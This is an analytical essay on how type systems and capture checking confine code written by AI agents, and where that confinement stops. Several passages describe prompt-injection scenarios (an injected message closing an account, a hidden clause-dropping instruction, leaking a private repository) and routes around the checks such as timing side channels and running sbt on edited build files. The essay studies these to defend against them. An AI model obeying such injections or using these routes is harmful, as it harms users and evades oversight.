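Coding agents use these features often. *Mining Type Constructs Using Patterns in AI-Generated Code* (Lee, Ul Hassan and Hindle, 2026) compared 545 pull requests (proposed code changes) by coding agents with 269 by people, all involving TypeScript's types. The agents added `any` an average of 2.16 times per pull request, compared with 0.24 times for people. Agents also used more type assertions and non-null assertions.

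Among the agents, Cursor added `any` about two and a half times as often as it removed it, while GitHub Copilot removed it more often than it added it. The counts are per pull request, not per line of code, so part of the gap between agents and people may reflect differences in the size of their changes. The data are from 2025 or earlier. Lee and colleagues conclude that agents put successful compilation ahead of type soundness. That would fit the numbers, but requests to convert old JavaScript code would produce a similar pattern.

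Evidence from lower-level code supports the same conclusion. *Can LLMs be Effective Code Contributors?* (2026) ran static analysis on code that models wrote for open-source projects. Unsafe casts were the most common type of problem for two of the three models, making up 40.3% of the 159 issues in GPT-4o's code and 36.9% of the 188 in Ministral3's. The share was only 9.3% for Qwen3-Coder, but many of its contributions were empty or incomplete. In the paper's example, a line stores a memory address where a single character belongs, which looks like a mistake rather than an attempt to get past a checker.

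An attacker needs only one escape hatch, so whether models can use one matters more for a safety layer than how often they do. Rejecting every snippet that contains `any` or an assertion would help, but it would not catch the refund from an empty list, which contains neither. TypeScript's types also do not record effects, so even a sound version of the language would guarantee only the shape of an action. A sandbox would have to limit what the action has the authority to do.

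### What happens outside the types

Capture checking does not cover other programs that a snippet starts, such as a version-control tool. For these, TACIT's guarantee is only as good as its list of permitted commands.

That list is hard to choose well. Odersky and colleagues recommend restricting it to specific safe commands and give `git diff` and `sbt` as examples. But `sbt`, Scala's build tool, executes code from the project's build files. An agent allowed to edit those files and run `sbt` can therefore execute code that no safe-mode compiler has checked. A sandbox around the whole process would limit the damage.

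Information can also leave a program without any explicit output. A pure function inside `map` cannot print a secret, but it can take longer for some secrets than for others. The snippet's running time, or whether it finishes at all, could then reveal something about the secret to the cloud model that wrote it. Odersky and colleagues exclude such side channels from their guarantee. One measurement might reveal a single bit, which is enough to answer a yes-or-no question about a confidential document. A long key would take many measurements, so it would help to limit the number of requests, which Odersky and colleagues mention as something TACIT's library could add.

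Types also don't limit how much time, memory or money a snippet uses. Snippets in LACUNA can keep calling `agent`, and the type checker cannot distinguish a long task from an endless one. Zhao and colleagues therefore limited the nesting to 128 levels and each research question to ten minutes. The developer has to choose such limits, and one that is too low will cut off useful work.

### Authority that is too wide

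A type system can hold a snippet to the permissions it was given, but it cannot determine which permissions the task needs. Under the principle of least privilege, each piece of code gets only the authority its job requires. Zhao and colleagues write that developers have to supply least privilege themselves, and that the type system "enforces it but does not infer it".

In the shop, refunding a duplicate charge requires `findCharges` and `refund`. If the developer leaves `cancelAccount` in scope because all three tools are in the same file, an injected message can lead the model to write well-typed code that closes the account. If any code can create a `Customer` value, a snippet can look up the charges of people who never contacted the shop.

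Even the two necessary tools allow too much. `refund` accepts any of the customer's charges and any amount. The developer could replace it with a tool that checks that a charge is a duplicate and refunds exactly what the customer paid. An attacker could then gain very little, but the developer would need to add another tool for refunding damaged items.

Wrapping data involves the same compromise. VirtusLab warns against classifying too much data, since agents are useful largely because they can read and understand files, emails and web pages. Forbidding an agent to read any of this content protects it from injections but also prevents it from resolving most complaints.

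### How far the guarantee is independent of the model

Odersky and colleagues describe TACIT's security guarantee as independent of the model, which is right for the property they tested. The compiler rejects any function that could send the wrapped secret out, whether the code comes from a careful model, a confused one or one working for the attacker. Without the wrapper, safety depended on how well each model had learned to refuse. The guarantee also holds for future models, provided that the trusted parts work and the attacker does not use a side channel.

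But they also claim more broadly in their threat model that an injection causing real harm must either move private data to an unauthorized destination or trigger a capability the agent was not given. The shop's wrongly refunded charge is a counterexample, because the shop loses money even though no private data goes anywhere and the agent uses only a tool it was granted.

Zhao and colleagues, who include all the researchers behind TACIT, state that types do not prevent this. Whether such an attack succeeds depends on the model's judgment. Of the eight successful attacks in their AgentDojo trials, seven were against Gemini 2.5 Pro and one was against o4-mini-high, though eight cases are too few to rank the two models.

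The worst that a snippet can do is the same for every model, and the developer sets that limit by choosing what is in scope. How often an attacker achieves that worst case still depends on the model, so better resistance to injections remains useful even with a sound type checker, especially for tools that move money or whose effects cannot be undone.

The same applies to the trusted local model. Suppose a confidential contract contains a hidden instruction to leave one clause out of any summary. If the local model follows it, the user reads a summary without that clause, even though the contract's text stays in its wrapper and the summary has the required type, `Classified[String]`.

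## Why can a well-typed action still be the wrong one?

An instruction usually calls for one particular action, but many programs can have the same type. If a shop wants its agent to refund a duplicate charge, the compiler checks only that the agent's code produces a `Receipt` using the names in scope. The type determines how many other programs would also pass.

### How many programs fit a type

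A function from a type with $m$ values to a type with $n$ values must return a result for each of the $m$ inputs, and it has $n$ results to choose from each time. That makes

$$n \times n \times \cdots \times n = n^m$$

possible functions. From `Bool` to `Bool` there are $2^2 = 4$: one returns its input, one returns the opposite, one always returns true and one always returns false. If the task is to negate the input, three of the four are wrong. For a type with three colors, there are $3^3 = 27$ functions that take a color and return a color. These figures count functions by their results, and a programmer can write each function in endlessly many ways.

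The compiler's check for missing cases does not reduce these numbers, because it only ensures that every input has some result. In Zhao and colleagues' example, the model had to name a color and left out blue. The compiler reported the missing case, but it would have accepted "red" as the name for blue.

For most actions, the types allow far more possible calls. The shop's `refund` tool takes a `Charge` and an `Int`, and an `Int` in Scala has $2^{32}$ possible values. If the customer has two charges, about 8.6 billion different refund calls are well-typed, and only one of them refunds the duplicate charge in full.

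Some types leave almost nothing open. Consider a pure function of type `A -> A` that has to work for every type `A` and always finish. The only one is the function that returns its argument unchanged. Wadler (1989), in *Theorems for Free!*, showed how to derive such facts from the type alone. The underlying principle, parametricity, is that a generic function has to treat all types alike, since it has no information about the values it receives. For a function $f$ of type `A -> A`, it implies that

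$$g(f(x)) = f(g(x))$$

for any function $g$ from one type to another. In other words, it makes no difference whether a program converts a value before or after applying $f$. Now let $g$ start from a type with a single value $u$ and send it to some value $b$ of any other type. Since $f(u)$ can only be $u$,

$$f(b) = f(g(u)) = g(f(u)) = g(u) = b.$$

Exactly two such functions have the type `(A, A) -> A`. Applied to (true, false), such a function $f$ returns either true or false. Suppose it returns true. For any two values $x$ and $y$, let $g$ send true to $x$ and false to $y$. Then $f(x, y) = g(f(\text{true}, \text{false})) = g(\text{true}) = x$, so $f$ always returns its first argument. If it returns false instead, it always returns its second. This result is slightly weaker in Scala, where generic code can call `toString` on any value and so could return whichever argument's string comes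 first alphabetically.

With lists, the number of functions that fit a type becomes unlimited again. A function of type `List[Int] -> List[Int]` can sort the list, reverse it or return an empty one. The generic type `List[A] -> List[A]` excludes sorting, because the function cannot compare elements of an unknown type, but it still allows the other two. Making a type more generic can also exclude the program the task requires. To find a duplicate charge, a snippet has to read order numbers, which it can do with a `List[Charge]` but not with a `List[A]`.

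These counts are not error rates, because a language model doesn't pick at random among the programs that fit the type, and it may choose the right one nearly every time. But when it chooses a wrong program that fits the type, the compiler can't detect the mistake. Zhao and colleagues name three such failures: the wrong algorithm, the wrong tool and a plausible but incorrect value.

### The wrong algorithm

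Suppose the shop compensates customers with vouchers worth $1, $3 and $4, and asks for a function that covers an amount with as few vouchers as possible. A model might write:

```
def vouchers(amount: Int): List[Int] =
  if amount == 0 then Nil
  else
    val v = List(4, 3, 1).find(_ <= amount).get
    v :: vouchers(amount - v)
```

This is a greedy algorithm, which always takes the largest voucher that fits. For $6 it returns 4, 1 and 1, although two $3 vouchers would do. The correct method is dynamic programming, which finds the best answer for $1, $2, $3 and so on, building each from the earlier ones. For $6 it tries adding one voucher to the best answers for $5, $3 and $2, and chooses $3, which needs only one voucher, for a total of two. Both functions have the type `Int => List[Int]`. The greedy one is right for every amount up to $5, so a quick trial could easily miss the mistake.

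*Evaluating and Improving LLM-based Competitive Program Generation* (Wei, Li and colleagues, 2025) tested DeepSeek-R1 on 80 programming contest problems in C++. Only 5 of its programs were correct. Of the other 75, 63 gave wrong answers, 5 were too slow and 7 did not compile. Experienced contestants examined the failed programs, many of which had several errors, and classified the errors. Incorrect algorithms made up 12.4% of the errors, misunderstood requirements 10.6% and mishandled edge cases 8.7%. A typical incorrect algorithm was a greedy one for a problem that needs dynamic programming.

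One of the misunderstood problems asked for a permutation, a list that contains each number exactly once. The model's program filled the list with alternating ones and twos. The result was still a list of integers, so its type was correct.

DeepSeek-R1 is an old model, and current ones do far better at contest problems, but a comparison within the study will probably hold up better. When Wei and colleagues gave the model targeted hints about its errors, it then solved 6 of the 7 problems where its program had not compiled, but only 33 of the 63 where its program had given a wrong answer. Someone or something also had to diagnose the errors to provide those hints, whereas a compiler produces its own error messages.

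### The wrong tool

The shop's `refund` and `cancelAccount` take different arguments, so a model cannot confuse them by changing only the name. Real tools can be harder to tell apart. The retail tools that Odersky and colleagues adapted for TACIT include these two:

```
def modifyPendingOrderItems(orderId: String,
  itemIds: List[String], newItemIds: List[String],
  paymentMethodId: String): Order
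def exchangeDeliveredOrderItems(orderId: String,
  itemIds: List[String], newItemIds: List[String],
  paymentMethodId: String): Order
```

Two of the shop's functions have identical types, but one changes a pending order and the other exchanges items the customer has already received. Swapping their names in any program leaves it well-typed. The same is true of `cancelPendingOrder` and `modifyPendingOrderPayment`, which both take two strings and return an `Order`. The shop's server may reject a call that doesn't suit the order's status, but only once the snippet is running.

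Sometimes the right call and the wrong call would both succeed. `modifyPendingOrderAddress` changes the address for one order, and `modifyUserAddress` changes the address in the customer's profile. Each takes an identifier and six strings for the address. If a customer wants one package sent to the office and the agent calls the wrong tool, the profile address will change and the package will still go to the customer's home. The calls return different types, `Order` and `User`, but the difference only matters if the snippet uses the result. Many snippets would ignore it and tell the customer that the address has been changed.

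Capture checking doesn't help here either, because the agent needs permission to use both tools. Only their names and descriptions indicate which one is appropriate.

### A plausible wrong value

A snippet can also call the right tool with the wrong arguments. All seven parameters of `modifyPendingOrderAddress` are strings, so the compiler accepts the same seven values in any of $7! = 5{,}040$ orders. The server would probably reject an order ID passed as the zip code, but it might accept a swapped city and state.

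Numbers have no units unless the developer gives them a type that records one. The shop stores amounts in cents. If the customer writes "I was charged $45 twice", the model might write:

```
refund(duplicate, 45)
```

The customer then gets 45 cents. *A Survey of Bugs in AI-Generated Code* (Gao, Tahir and colleagues, 2026) describes a similar mistake in a model-written blockchain contract. The lease it was based on stated all amounts in US dollars, but the program treated them as Ether, a cryptocurrency.

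A type can even prompt a model to invent a value. In Zhao and colleagues' example, an agent emails a coworker a reminder about a meeting. The model's code takes the time from the first match in the agent's memory, which may be the wrong meeting if there are several. The search may also find nothing, and the types force the program to handle that case. The model does so by supplying "TBD", which the compiler accepts because it is a string. If there is no match, the coworker receives an email that gives the time as TBD. Stopping with an error or asking the user would have been better, but a default value satisfies the type equally well.

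### Missing steps and the wrong order

Many actions return nothing of interest, and in Scala their result type is `Unit`, whose only value is `()`. When a developer calls `agent[Unit]("remember the team sync is Friday at 3pm")`, the model should write code that stores the meeting. But the snippet `()` also has type `Unit`, and it does nothing. It passes the type check because an action's type limits which effects the action may have but doesn't require any of them.

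The same gap lets a snippet omit part of its work. An agent can refund a charge without checking whether the shop's policy permits it, because `refund` doesn't require evidence of a check. Nogueira and colleagues observed that models' programs often lack basic checks on their input, such as a limit on how much they read into memory.

Types constrain the order of two calls only if one needs the other's result. A snippet cannot refund a charge before it has called `findCharges`, since it would have no `Charge` to pass. But suppose a customer wants a refund and then wants to close the account:

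```
cancelAccount(customer)
val charges = findCharges(customer)
refund(charges.last, charges.last.amount)
```

This code is well-typed even if closing an account deletes its charges. In that case the last line fails, and the customer loses both the account and the refund.

### What retrying does to the remaining mistakes

LACUNA asks the model for new code only when the compiler rejects a snippet. As Zhao and colleagues point out, this retry loop therefore does nothing about the failures described above, though it changes how common they are among the snippets that run.

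Suppose that out of 100 snippets, 70 are right, 20 are ill-typed and 10 are well-typed but wrong. Suppose also that the ill-typed ones would stop with an error if they ran, and that the wrong ones would finish without one. If the system rejects the ill-typed snippets and asks again, and the model's new attempts have the same rates, the results are:

| | Right | Error reported | Wrong, no error |
|---|---|---|---|
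| No type check | 70 | 20 | 10 |
| Type check, one attempt | 70 | 20 | 10 |
| Type check, three attempts | 86.8 | 0.8 | 12.4 |
| Type check, unlimited attempts | 87.5 | 0 | 12.5 |

With unlimited attempts, every task ends with a well-typed snippet, and 70 out of every 80 of these are correct. In general, if a share $r$ of the model's snippets is correct and a share $w$ is well-typed but wrong, then $r/(r+w)$ of the final snippets are correct.

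Total failures fall from 30 to 12.5, but unnoticed mistakes rise from 10 to 12.5 because some retries replace an ill-typed snippet with a well-typed wrong one. A type check with one attempt has the same totals as no check, but the 20 rejected snippets never run, so they cannot do any damage before they fail. A developer who worries more about unnoticed mistakes than about interruptions could therefore skip the retries and pass rejected tasks to a person.

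The model's rates will rarely stay the same, since a task that led to one mistake may lead to another. In experiments by Mündler and colleagues, software that prevented type errors let 15 more of Qwen2.5 32B's programs compile, and about 14 of them were correct. For Gemma 2 2B, 59 more compiled, but only about 7 were correct. If the 20 ill-typed snippets turned out like Qwen's programs, the total would be about 89 right and 11 wrong. If they turned out like Gemma's, it would be about 72 right and 28 wrong, nearly three times as many unnoticed mistakes as before.

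*From LLMs to Agents in Programming* (Kjellberg, Staron and Fotrousi, 2026) tested such a loop with 16 models on 699 tasks in C. A model whose program did not compile received the error message and could try again, for up to five rounds. The share of programs that compiled rose by between 5.3 and 79.4 percentage points, depending on the model. The programs' similarity to human-written solutions hardly changed, and the researchers conclude that the compiler's feedback did not affect what the programs do. The measurements cannot establish this, because the researchers did not run tests. Replacing a `*` with a `+` barely changes a similarity score, and a correct program can look quite unlike the reference solution.

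### Well-typed agents that fail their tasks

τ²-bench, the customer-service benchmark, gives an idea of how often agents fail even when all the code they run is well-typed. The agent has to fulfill a simulated customer's request while following a written policy, and it solves the task if the company's records end up as they should. Odersky and colleagues ran every task ten times with TACIT, which lets only well-typed snippets run:

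| Model | Domain | Snippets that needed a retry | Tasks solved |
|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | Airline | 1.58% | 45.2% |
| gpt-oss-120b | Retail | 0.32% | 57.0% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | Airline | 7.93% | 58.6% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | Retail | 1.57% | 75.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | Airline | 1.43% | 61.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | Retail | 0.33% | 77.5% |

The agents failed between 22.5% and 54.8% of the time. Difficulty with the type checker explains little of this, because the models seldom had to retry, and one or two retries were usually enough when they did. In the retail domain, gpt-oss-120b had the fewest rejected snippets of the three models but solved the fewest tasks. The typed interface does not explain the failures either, since the same models did slightly worse with ordinary tool calls. Odersky and colleagues list correctness among the things that TACIT does not aim to guarantee.

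LACUNA, by contrast, solved fewer tasks overall than the standard agent, which makes ordinary tool calls. The results of Zhao and colleagues by domain are:

| Domain | deepseek-v4-flash, LACUNA | deepseek-v4-flash, tool calls | gemini-3.1-flash-lite, LACUNA | gemini-3.1-flash-lite, tool calls |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Retail | 58.8% | 80.9% | 43.9% | 52.6% |
| Airline | 70.0% | 75.5% | 38.0% | 56.0% |
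| Telecom | 88.6% | 100.0% | 14.9% | 15.8% |
| Telecom workflow | 83.3% | 95.4% | 24.6% | 21.1% |
| All 392 tasks | 76.0% | 90.0% | 29.1% | 33.2% |

LACUNA did better than the standard agent in only one of the eight domain comparisons. Each task ran only once, so the smaller differences may be due to chance, but the overall gap for deepseek-v4-flash almost certainly isn't, because it covers 392 tasks. The standard agent solved all the telecom tasks, so the model was capable of solving the 13 that LACUNA failed.

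Type checking leaves much to the model, as repeated runs show. *τ-Emotion-Bench* (Singh, Saeidi and colleagues, 2026) tested agents on 580 service tasks with simulated customers who were, for example, angry or anxious. The best model, GLM-5.3, solved 78.6% of the tasks in an average run but only 66.5% in all three runs. It therefore succeeded in one run and failed in another on a substantial number of tasks, though it had the same tools and a type checker would have imposed the same limits each time.

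### Why a failed task is not always a wrong snippet

An agent can fail a task without running a wrong snippet, so not every unsolved task is a case of well-typed code doing the wrong thing. Zhao and colleagues ended a conversation after 40 customer messages, 200 steps, or 300 seconds in which nothing happened. A model that keeps writing code the compiler rejects, as gemini-3.1-flash-lite did in the telecom domain, will fail most of its tasks because it does nothing.

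The agent may misunderstand the customer or forget to ask for a detail, and then carry out the mistaken request perfectly. It can also fail by breaking the policy. According to *How Can Input Reformulation Improve Tool Usage Accuracy* (2025), an agent on the original τ-bench gets no credit in that case, even when it gives the customer what they asked for.

Small changes to the instructions can also affect the score. Some telecom tasks require the customer to do something on their own phone, and in one version of the benchmark, the agent is told to ask the customer to do this and not to attempt it itself. *J-tau* (2026), which adapts the benchmark to Japanese, suggests that this instruction explains that version's higher telecom scores.

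Simulated customers make mistakes too. For *τ-Knowledge* (2026), two annotators with customer service experience checked 194 conversations and found only 4 in which the simulated customer's errors could have prevented a correct agent from succeeding. *CUEing User Simulators* (2026) used a language model to determine the main cause of each failure on τ²-bench, and found a much larger share that were not the agent's fault. With human users, agents succeeded in 61% of conversations, or 75% when failures caused by the user or the test environment were excluded, which implies that the agent was responsible for only about half of the failures. The two results are not directly comparable, because the second also counts faults in the environment and relies on a model's judgment.

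The tests of TACIT and LACUNA may have included faulty retail and airline tasks that other researchers have since corrected. *SEATauBench* (Nguyen, Adila and colleagues, 2026) ran three models three times each on the corrected tasks. At least one of the nine runs succeeded on 92% of the airline tasks, 95.6% of the retail tasks and all the telecom tasks. At most a few of the corrected tasks can therefore be impossible, far too few to account for failure rates like those in the tables above.

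### Which mistakes agents make

Several recent studies sort agents' mistakes in ways that fit the distinction between shape and correctness. *Non-Collaborative User Simulators for Tool Agents* (2025) distinguishes three kinds of mistake on τ-bench, and Nguyen and colleagues use a similar list. The last column below gives the likely effect of a type checker.

| Mistake | Source | Would a type checker catch it? |
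|---|---|---|
| Reply in the wrong format | *Non-Collaborative User Simulators* | Yes |
| Call that does not match the tool's schema | Nguyen and colleagues | Yes |
| Wrong argument in a necessary call | Both | Only if the types differ |
| Calls in the wrong order | Nguyen and colleagues | Only if one call needs the other's result |
| Change to the records that the task did not require | *Non-Collaborative User Simulators* | No, if the tool is in scope |
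| Omission of a necessary action | Nguyen and colleagues | Rarely |

Singh and colleagues identify policy violations and unnecessary interaction with the customer as important ways agents fail. A type checker would prevent few failures of either kind, because a call that breaks the policy can be well-typed, and so can code that asks the customer for something the agent could have looked up.

Studies of ordinary programs support the same conclusion, though less clearly. Gao and colleagues reviewed 126 studies of bugs in AI-generated code, published up to June 2026. Functional bugs, where a program does something other than what it should, are mentioned in 83% of the studies, and syntax errors in 48%, but these percentages don't measure how common each kind of bug is. The functional category also includes some mistakes that a static type checker can catch. One of the survey's examples of a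 semantic bug is a Python function that crashes when it calls a string method on a number.

*Schema First Tool APIs for LLM Agents* (Sigdel and Baral, 2026) gave a model the same tools with either free-form documentation or formal schemas. With schemas, the model made fewer malformed calls, but no fewer well-formed calls that made no sense for the task. This was a small pilot study with one locally run model, which did not complete a single task under any condition, so it is weak evidence about capable agents.

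*Action-Space Shaping for LLM Agents* (2026) kept the tasks the same but renamed, merged or split the tools. Some models chose the right action but wrote it incorrectly, for example by using a tool's original name after it had changed. The researchers measured the effect by running those calls in the form evidently intended. A compiler with a retry loop is most promising for these mistakes, because only the form of the call needs correcting, but they occurred mainly in older models. Other errors were in the choice of action. Qwen2.5-7B tended to do more than the task required under almost every version of the tools, and a compiler would have accepted each extra call as long as its arguments had the right types.

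## How far can more precise types close the gap?

The shop's `refund` tool accepts billions of different calls, nearly all of them wrong. A developer can exclude most of the wrong calls by writing more precise types. These range from a single line of code to a complete description of the task. If the type is a complete description, whoever writes the program also has to prove that the program meets that description.

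### Different types for different things

Many of the shop's tools use `String` and `Int` for everything. In Scala, a library can define new types on top of them:

```
opaque type Cents = Int
opaque type City = String
opaque type ZipCode = String
```

While the program runs, a `Cents` value is an ordinary integer, so the new type adds no running time or memory use. But code outside the library cannot pass an `Int` to a function that takes `Cents`. If `refund` takes `Cents`, the call `refund(duplicate, 45)` no longer compiles. Mixed-up units can be expensive. Sternfeld, Kucharavy and Dolamic (2025), in *TypePilot*, recall that NASA lost the Mars Climate Orbiter in 1999 because one part of the software produced imperial units and another required metric ones.

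The tool `modifyPendingOrderAddress` takes seven strings, and a snippet compiles whatever order it passes them in. With a separate type for each parameter, only one order compiles. Swapping `cancelPendingOrder` and `modifyPendingOrderPayment` without changing the arguments also causes a compile error if the first requires a `Reason` and the second a `PaymentMethodId`.

More precise types work best for values that come from tools. `duplicate.amount` already has the type `Cents`, so the model can't give it the wrong one. When a value comes from the customer's message, the model has to choose the type itself, and mistakes such as `City("CA")`, or `Cents(45)` for a charge of $45, still compile.

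A library can also test a value before it attaches the label. In one program that Sternfeld and colleagues examined, a model had written a function for averaging a list of ages that accepted negative ages and returned 0 for an empty list. A revised version takes a list of `Age` values, which other code can create only through a function that rejects anything outside 0 to 120. Its new result type also makes the caller handle the empty list.

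The revision came from a three-step process in which one model call writes the program, a second lists its weaknesses, and a third rewrites it using Scala's type system. The researchers ran 15 checks on how the programs handled normal and unusual input. Qwen2.5-Coder 32B passed 8 with a plain prompt, 11 when the prompt recommended safe types, and all 15 with the full process. Part of the last gain probably came from the list of weaknesses rather than the types. CodeLlama 70B failed several checks under every condition, but both models are old.

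### Using a value once, and in the right order

An ordinary type checker accepts a snippet that closes a customer's account and then looks up the charges to refund. Making `Customer` a linear type prevents this, because a program must use a linear value exactly once. `cancelAccount(customer)` uses the value up, so a later `findCharges(customer)` does not compile. `findCharges` also uses up the value, so it has to return a new `Customer` along with the charges for the program to close the account afterwards.

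If `Charge` is also linear, a snippet cannot refund the same charge twice. But the next snippet can call `findCharges` again and get a new value for the same charge, so the shop still needs a record of past refunds.

Typestate puts an object's current state into its type. The tools `modifyPendingOrderItems` and `exchangeDeliveredOrderItems` currently have identical types. If one requires an `Order[Pending]` and the other an `Order[Delivered]`, the type checker rejects a snippet that uses one in place of the other. The shop's server must still check the status, because an order may ship after the snippet looks it up but before the snippet changes it.

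Fonseca, in *AeonBox*, uses linear types to stop a coding agent from leaking private code. The agent can use GitHub only through functions like these, here simplified:

```
def readRepo (1 s: Session) (r: Repo) :
  {s2: Session | tainted s2 = (isPrivate r || tainted s)}
def createPublicIssue (1 s: {s: Session | tainted s = false})
  (text: String) : Issue
```

The `1` marks a parameter that the function uses up, and the conditions in braces restrict which sessions the function accepts or returns. Reading a repository uses up the session and returns a new one, which is tainted if the repository is private or the old session was tainted. Creating a public issue requires an untainted session.

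Suppose a planted instruction leads the model to write a program that reads a private repository and posts the contents publicly. Reading the repository leaves the program with only a tainted session, which it can't use to post publicly, so the program does not compile. If sessions were not linear, the program could keep the old, clean session and post with that.

According to Fonseca, no prompt can make the agent leak data "within the boundaries we modeled". The post supports this with a worked example but no trials. The rule also blocks some harmless actions. Once the agent has read anything private, it can't open a public issue, even about something unrelated.

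*Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents* (Kamath, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) presents Agent-C, which enforces such rules at run time instead. A developer might require the agent to identify the customer and confirm that an order is theirs before reading it. Agent-C checks every proposed tool call against the rules before it runs, and makes the model try again if the call breaks one. Because Agent-C can consult the shop's records, it can also require refunds to go to the original payment method or a gift card. Without Agent-C, Claude Sonnet 4.5 tried to send a refund to a different account when a customer insisted, although the prompt forbade this.

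On retail and airline tasks, Agent-C raised Claude Sonnet 4.5's compliance with the rules from 77.4% to 100%. The share of tasks the agent completed without breaking a rule rose only from 71.8% to 75.2%. With Agent-C, about a quarter of the tasks therefore failed even though the agent obeyed every rule.

### Conditions on values

The braces in Fonseca's functions contain refinement types, which attach a logical condition to an ordinary type. Bovel, Kunčak and Odersky (2026), in *First-Class Refinement Types for Scala*, present a prototype that adds them to the Scala 3 compiler. With their notation, the shop could declare its tools like this:

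```
def refund(charge: Charge,
  amount: {n: Int with n <= charge.amount}): Refund
def cancelAccount(customer: Customer): Cancellation

def handle(customer: Customer): Refund =
  agent("The customer paid twice for one order. Refund the duplicate.")
```

Both tools used to return a `Receipt`. Now `cancelAccount(customer)` does not compile as an answer to this request, because a `Cancellation` is not a `Refund`. A snippet could still cancel the account on one line, ignore the result and return a refund on the next. To prevent that, the developer has to remove `cancelAccount` from scope or make it require a capability that the snippet lacks.

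The amount can no longer exceed the charge. In `refund(duplicate, duplicate.amount)`, the checker only has to prove that a number is no greater than itself. It rejects `refund(duplicate, 4500)`, because it cannot know the size of the charge before the program runs. The snippet can test this first:

```
if 4500 <= duplicate.amount then refund(duplicate, 4500)
else throw Exception("The charge is smaller than that.")
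```

The call compiles inside the first branch because the checker treats the tested condition as true there. The snippet can also use an automatic run-time check, which raises an exception if the condition fails, but earlier lines may already have had side effects by then.

The checker enforces only the conditions that the developer thought to write into the types. Suppose the type of `charge.amount` also records that every charge is positive. The checker can then prove that −4,500 cents is less than the charge, so it accepts a refund of minus $45. To prevent this, the developer also needs to set a lower bound on the refund.

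A refund of the wrong charge also compiles:

```
val charge = findCharges(customer).head
refund(charge, charge.amount)
```

This refunds the first charge on the list, whatever it was for. The developer could add a condition that the list contains an earlier charge with the same order number. But that is the test the snippet was supposed to provide, so the developer has done most of the task by hand. The condition may also be wrong, since a customer who pays for an order in two installments has two legitimate charges with the same order number.

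Stricter types can lead a model to write code that makes up a plausible value. In Zhao and colleagues' example, a meeting reminder gave the time as "TBD", which is a valid string. A refinement type could require text in the form of a clock time. If no meeting was found, a good snippet would then stop with an error, but a bad one could satisfy the type with "15:00", which the recipient is more likely to believe.

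Bovel and colleagues have a computer-checked proof that the core of their system is sound, meaning that if an expression finishes, its value meets the condition. The prototype assumes, without checking, that any function used in a condition is pure and eventually finishes. The researchers suggest that capture checking could later enforce purity.

Refinement types can also limit what code is allowed to do. *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (Metere, 2026) applies them to agent skills, which are packages of instructions and scripts. Each skill comes with a list of the capabilities it may use, and the type checker rejects any tool call that needs an unlisted capability. The method doesn't check whether the list is longer than necessary or whether a permitted call is the right one.

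### Types that describe the whole task

A refinement checker usually proves its conditions automatically, which restricts it to conditions a solver can handle. In languages with dependent types, such as Lean, types can contain any mathematical statement about a program's values, but the author of the program has to supply the proof.

Sorting a list shows how much such a type can settle. A first attempt might require the output to be in ascending order:

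```
def sort (xs : List Int) : {ys : List Int // Ascending ys}
```

A function that always returns the empty list has this type, because an empty list has no elements out of order. The missing requirement is that the output must be a permutation of the input, with the same elements the same number of times:

```
def sort (xs : List Int) :
  {ys : List Int // Ascending ys ∧ Permutation xs ys}
```

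Now each input has only one possible output, because an ascending permutation has to begin with the smallest element, then continue with the smallest of those that remain, and so on. All functions of this type therefore return the same results.

Sorting programs that satisfy the same type can still differ in how long they take. One could try every possible order of the list until it finds an ascending one. A list of 20 different numbers has about $2.4 \times 10^{18}$ orders, so at a billion per second the program could need 77 years. A type can also bound the number of steps, but then the developer has to define a step and whoever writes the code has to prove the bound.

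*Agentic Verified Optimization of Real-World Software* (2026) uses this separation. Agents receive a slow but simple Lean function $f$ and must write a faster one, $f'$, with a proof that $f = f'$ for all valid inputs. The simple function is the specification. Lean checks that the results stay the same, and the researchers measure speed by running both versions.

A complete specification would also catch the greedy voucher algorithm, which covers $6 with vouchers for $4, $1 and $1 when two $3 vouchers would be enough. The algorithm passes if the type only requires the vouchers to add up to the right amount. If the type also requires that no shorter list of vouchers adds up to that amount, the algorithm can't pass, because there is no proof that it meets this requirement.

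### Why checking a proof is type checking

In Lean, a statement is a type, and a proof of the statement is a value of that type. The encyclopedia article *Lean (proof assistant)* gives a short example, which looks like this with different names:

```
theorem swap (a b : Prop) : a ∧ b → b ∧ a :=
  fun ⟨ha, hb⟩ => ⟨hb, ha⟩
```

The first line states that if $a$ and $b$ are both true, then $b$ and $a$ are both true. A proof of $a \wedge b$ is a pair of proofs, one of $a$ and one of $b$. The second line is a function that takes such a pair and returns it in the opposite order. If it returned the pair unchanged, Lean would report a type error, as Scala does when a snippet passes a customer to a function that needs a charge.

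When types are logical statements, the typing rule for function calls becomes the rule that if $A$ implies $B$ and $A$ is true, then $B$ is true.

*Lean*, a set of lecture notes by Subramanian (2026), describes how a small trusted program, the kernel, checks proofs from untrusted sources. As with Necula's proof-carrying code, the check does not depend on who wrote the proof.

That is why a type check could certify some of the most difficult mathematics of 2026. *The part of Navier-Stokes no one is talking about* (2026) points out that when OpenAI solved the Navier–Stokes problem, a question about fluid flow, it published a Lean proof along with the readable one. In November, an AI-written Lean proof of the Riemann hypothesis appeared. Anthropic's Lean proof of Fermat's Last Theorem runs to 13 million lines, far more than anyone could review by hand.

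The kernel has to be correct, however. *Riemann con leche* (Breitner, 2026) reports that AI models found a number of bugs in Lean's kernel and in other proof checkers in 2026. Breitner has not seen an AI agent exploit such a bug unless asked to. In response to the bugs, Breitner supervised Claude in building con-leche, a checker that comes with a proof that it never accepts a proof of a false statement. Mathematicians used it on the Riemann hypothesis. *Lean Now Ships with Verified Kernels* (De Moura, 2026) notes that con-leche's correctness proof assumes the consistency of set theory and that bugs in the compiler could still matter. Lean can now run several independent checkers on the same proof, which helps because they are unlikely to share a bug.

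### What models can prove about programs

Until recently, proofs took far too much work for most software. Langley (2026), in *We have proof automation now*, cites seL4, a verified operating-system kernel whose developers spent about ten times as long on the proofs as on design and programming. Langley expects language models to change this, because once the statement is right, any proof of it will do, whatever its style.

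In *A benchmark for vericoding*, Bursuc, Ehrenborg and colleagues (2025) measured how well models could write both a program and its proof from a formal specification, usually with five attempts. The tasks used Lean, Dafny and Verus. Dafny and Verus automate more of the proof than Lean does, and Verus checks Rust programs.

| Language | Best single model | Solved by at least one of nine models |
|---|---|---|
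| Dafny | 68% (Claude Opus 4.1) | 82% |
| Verus | 31% (GPT-5) | 44% |
| Lean | 18% (GPT-5) | 27% |

These models are more than a year old. On the simpler task of writing the proof for an existing Dafny program, the best result rose from 68% to 89% in just over a year.

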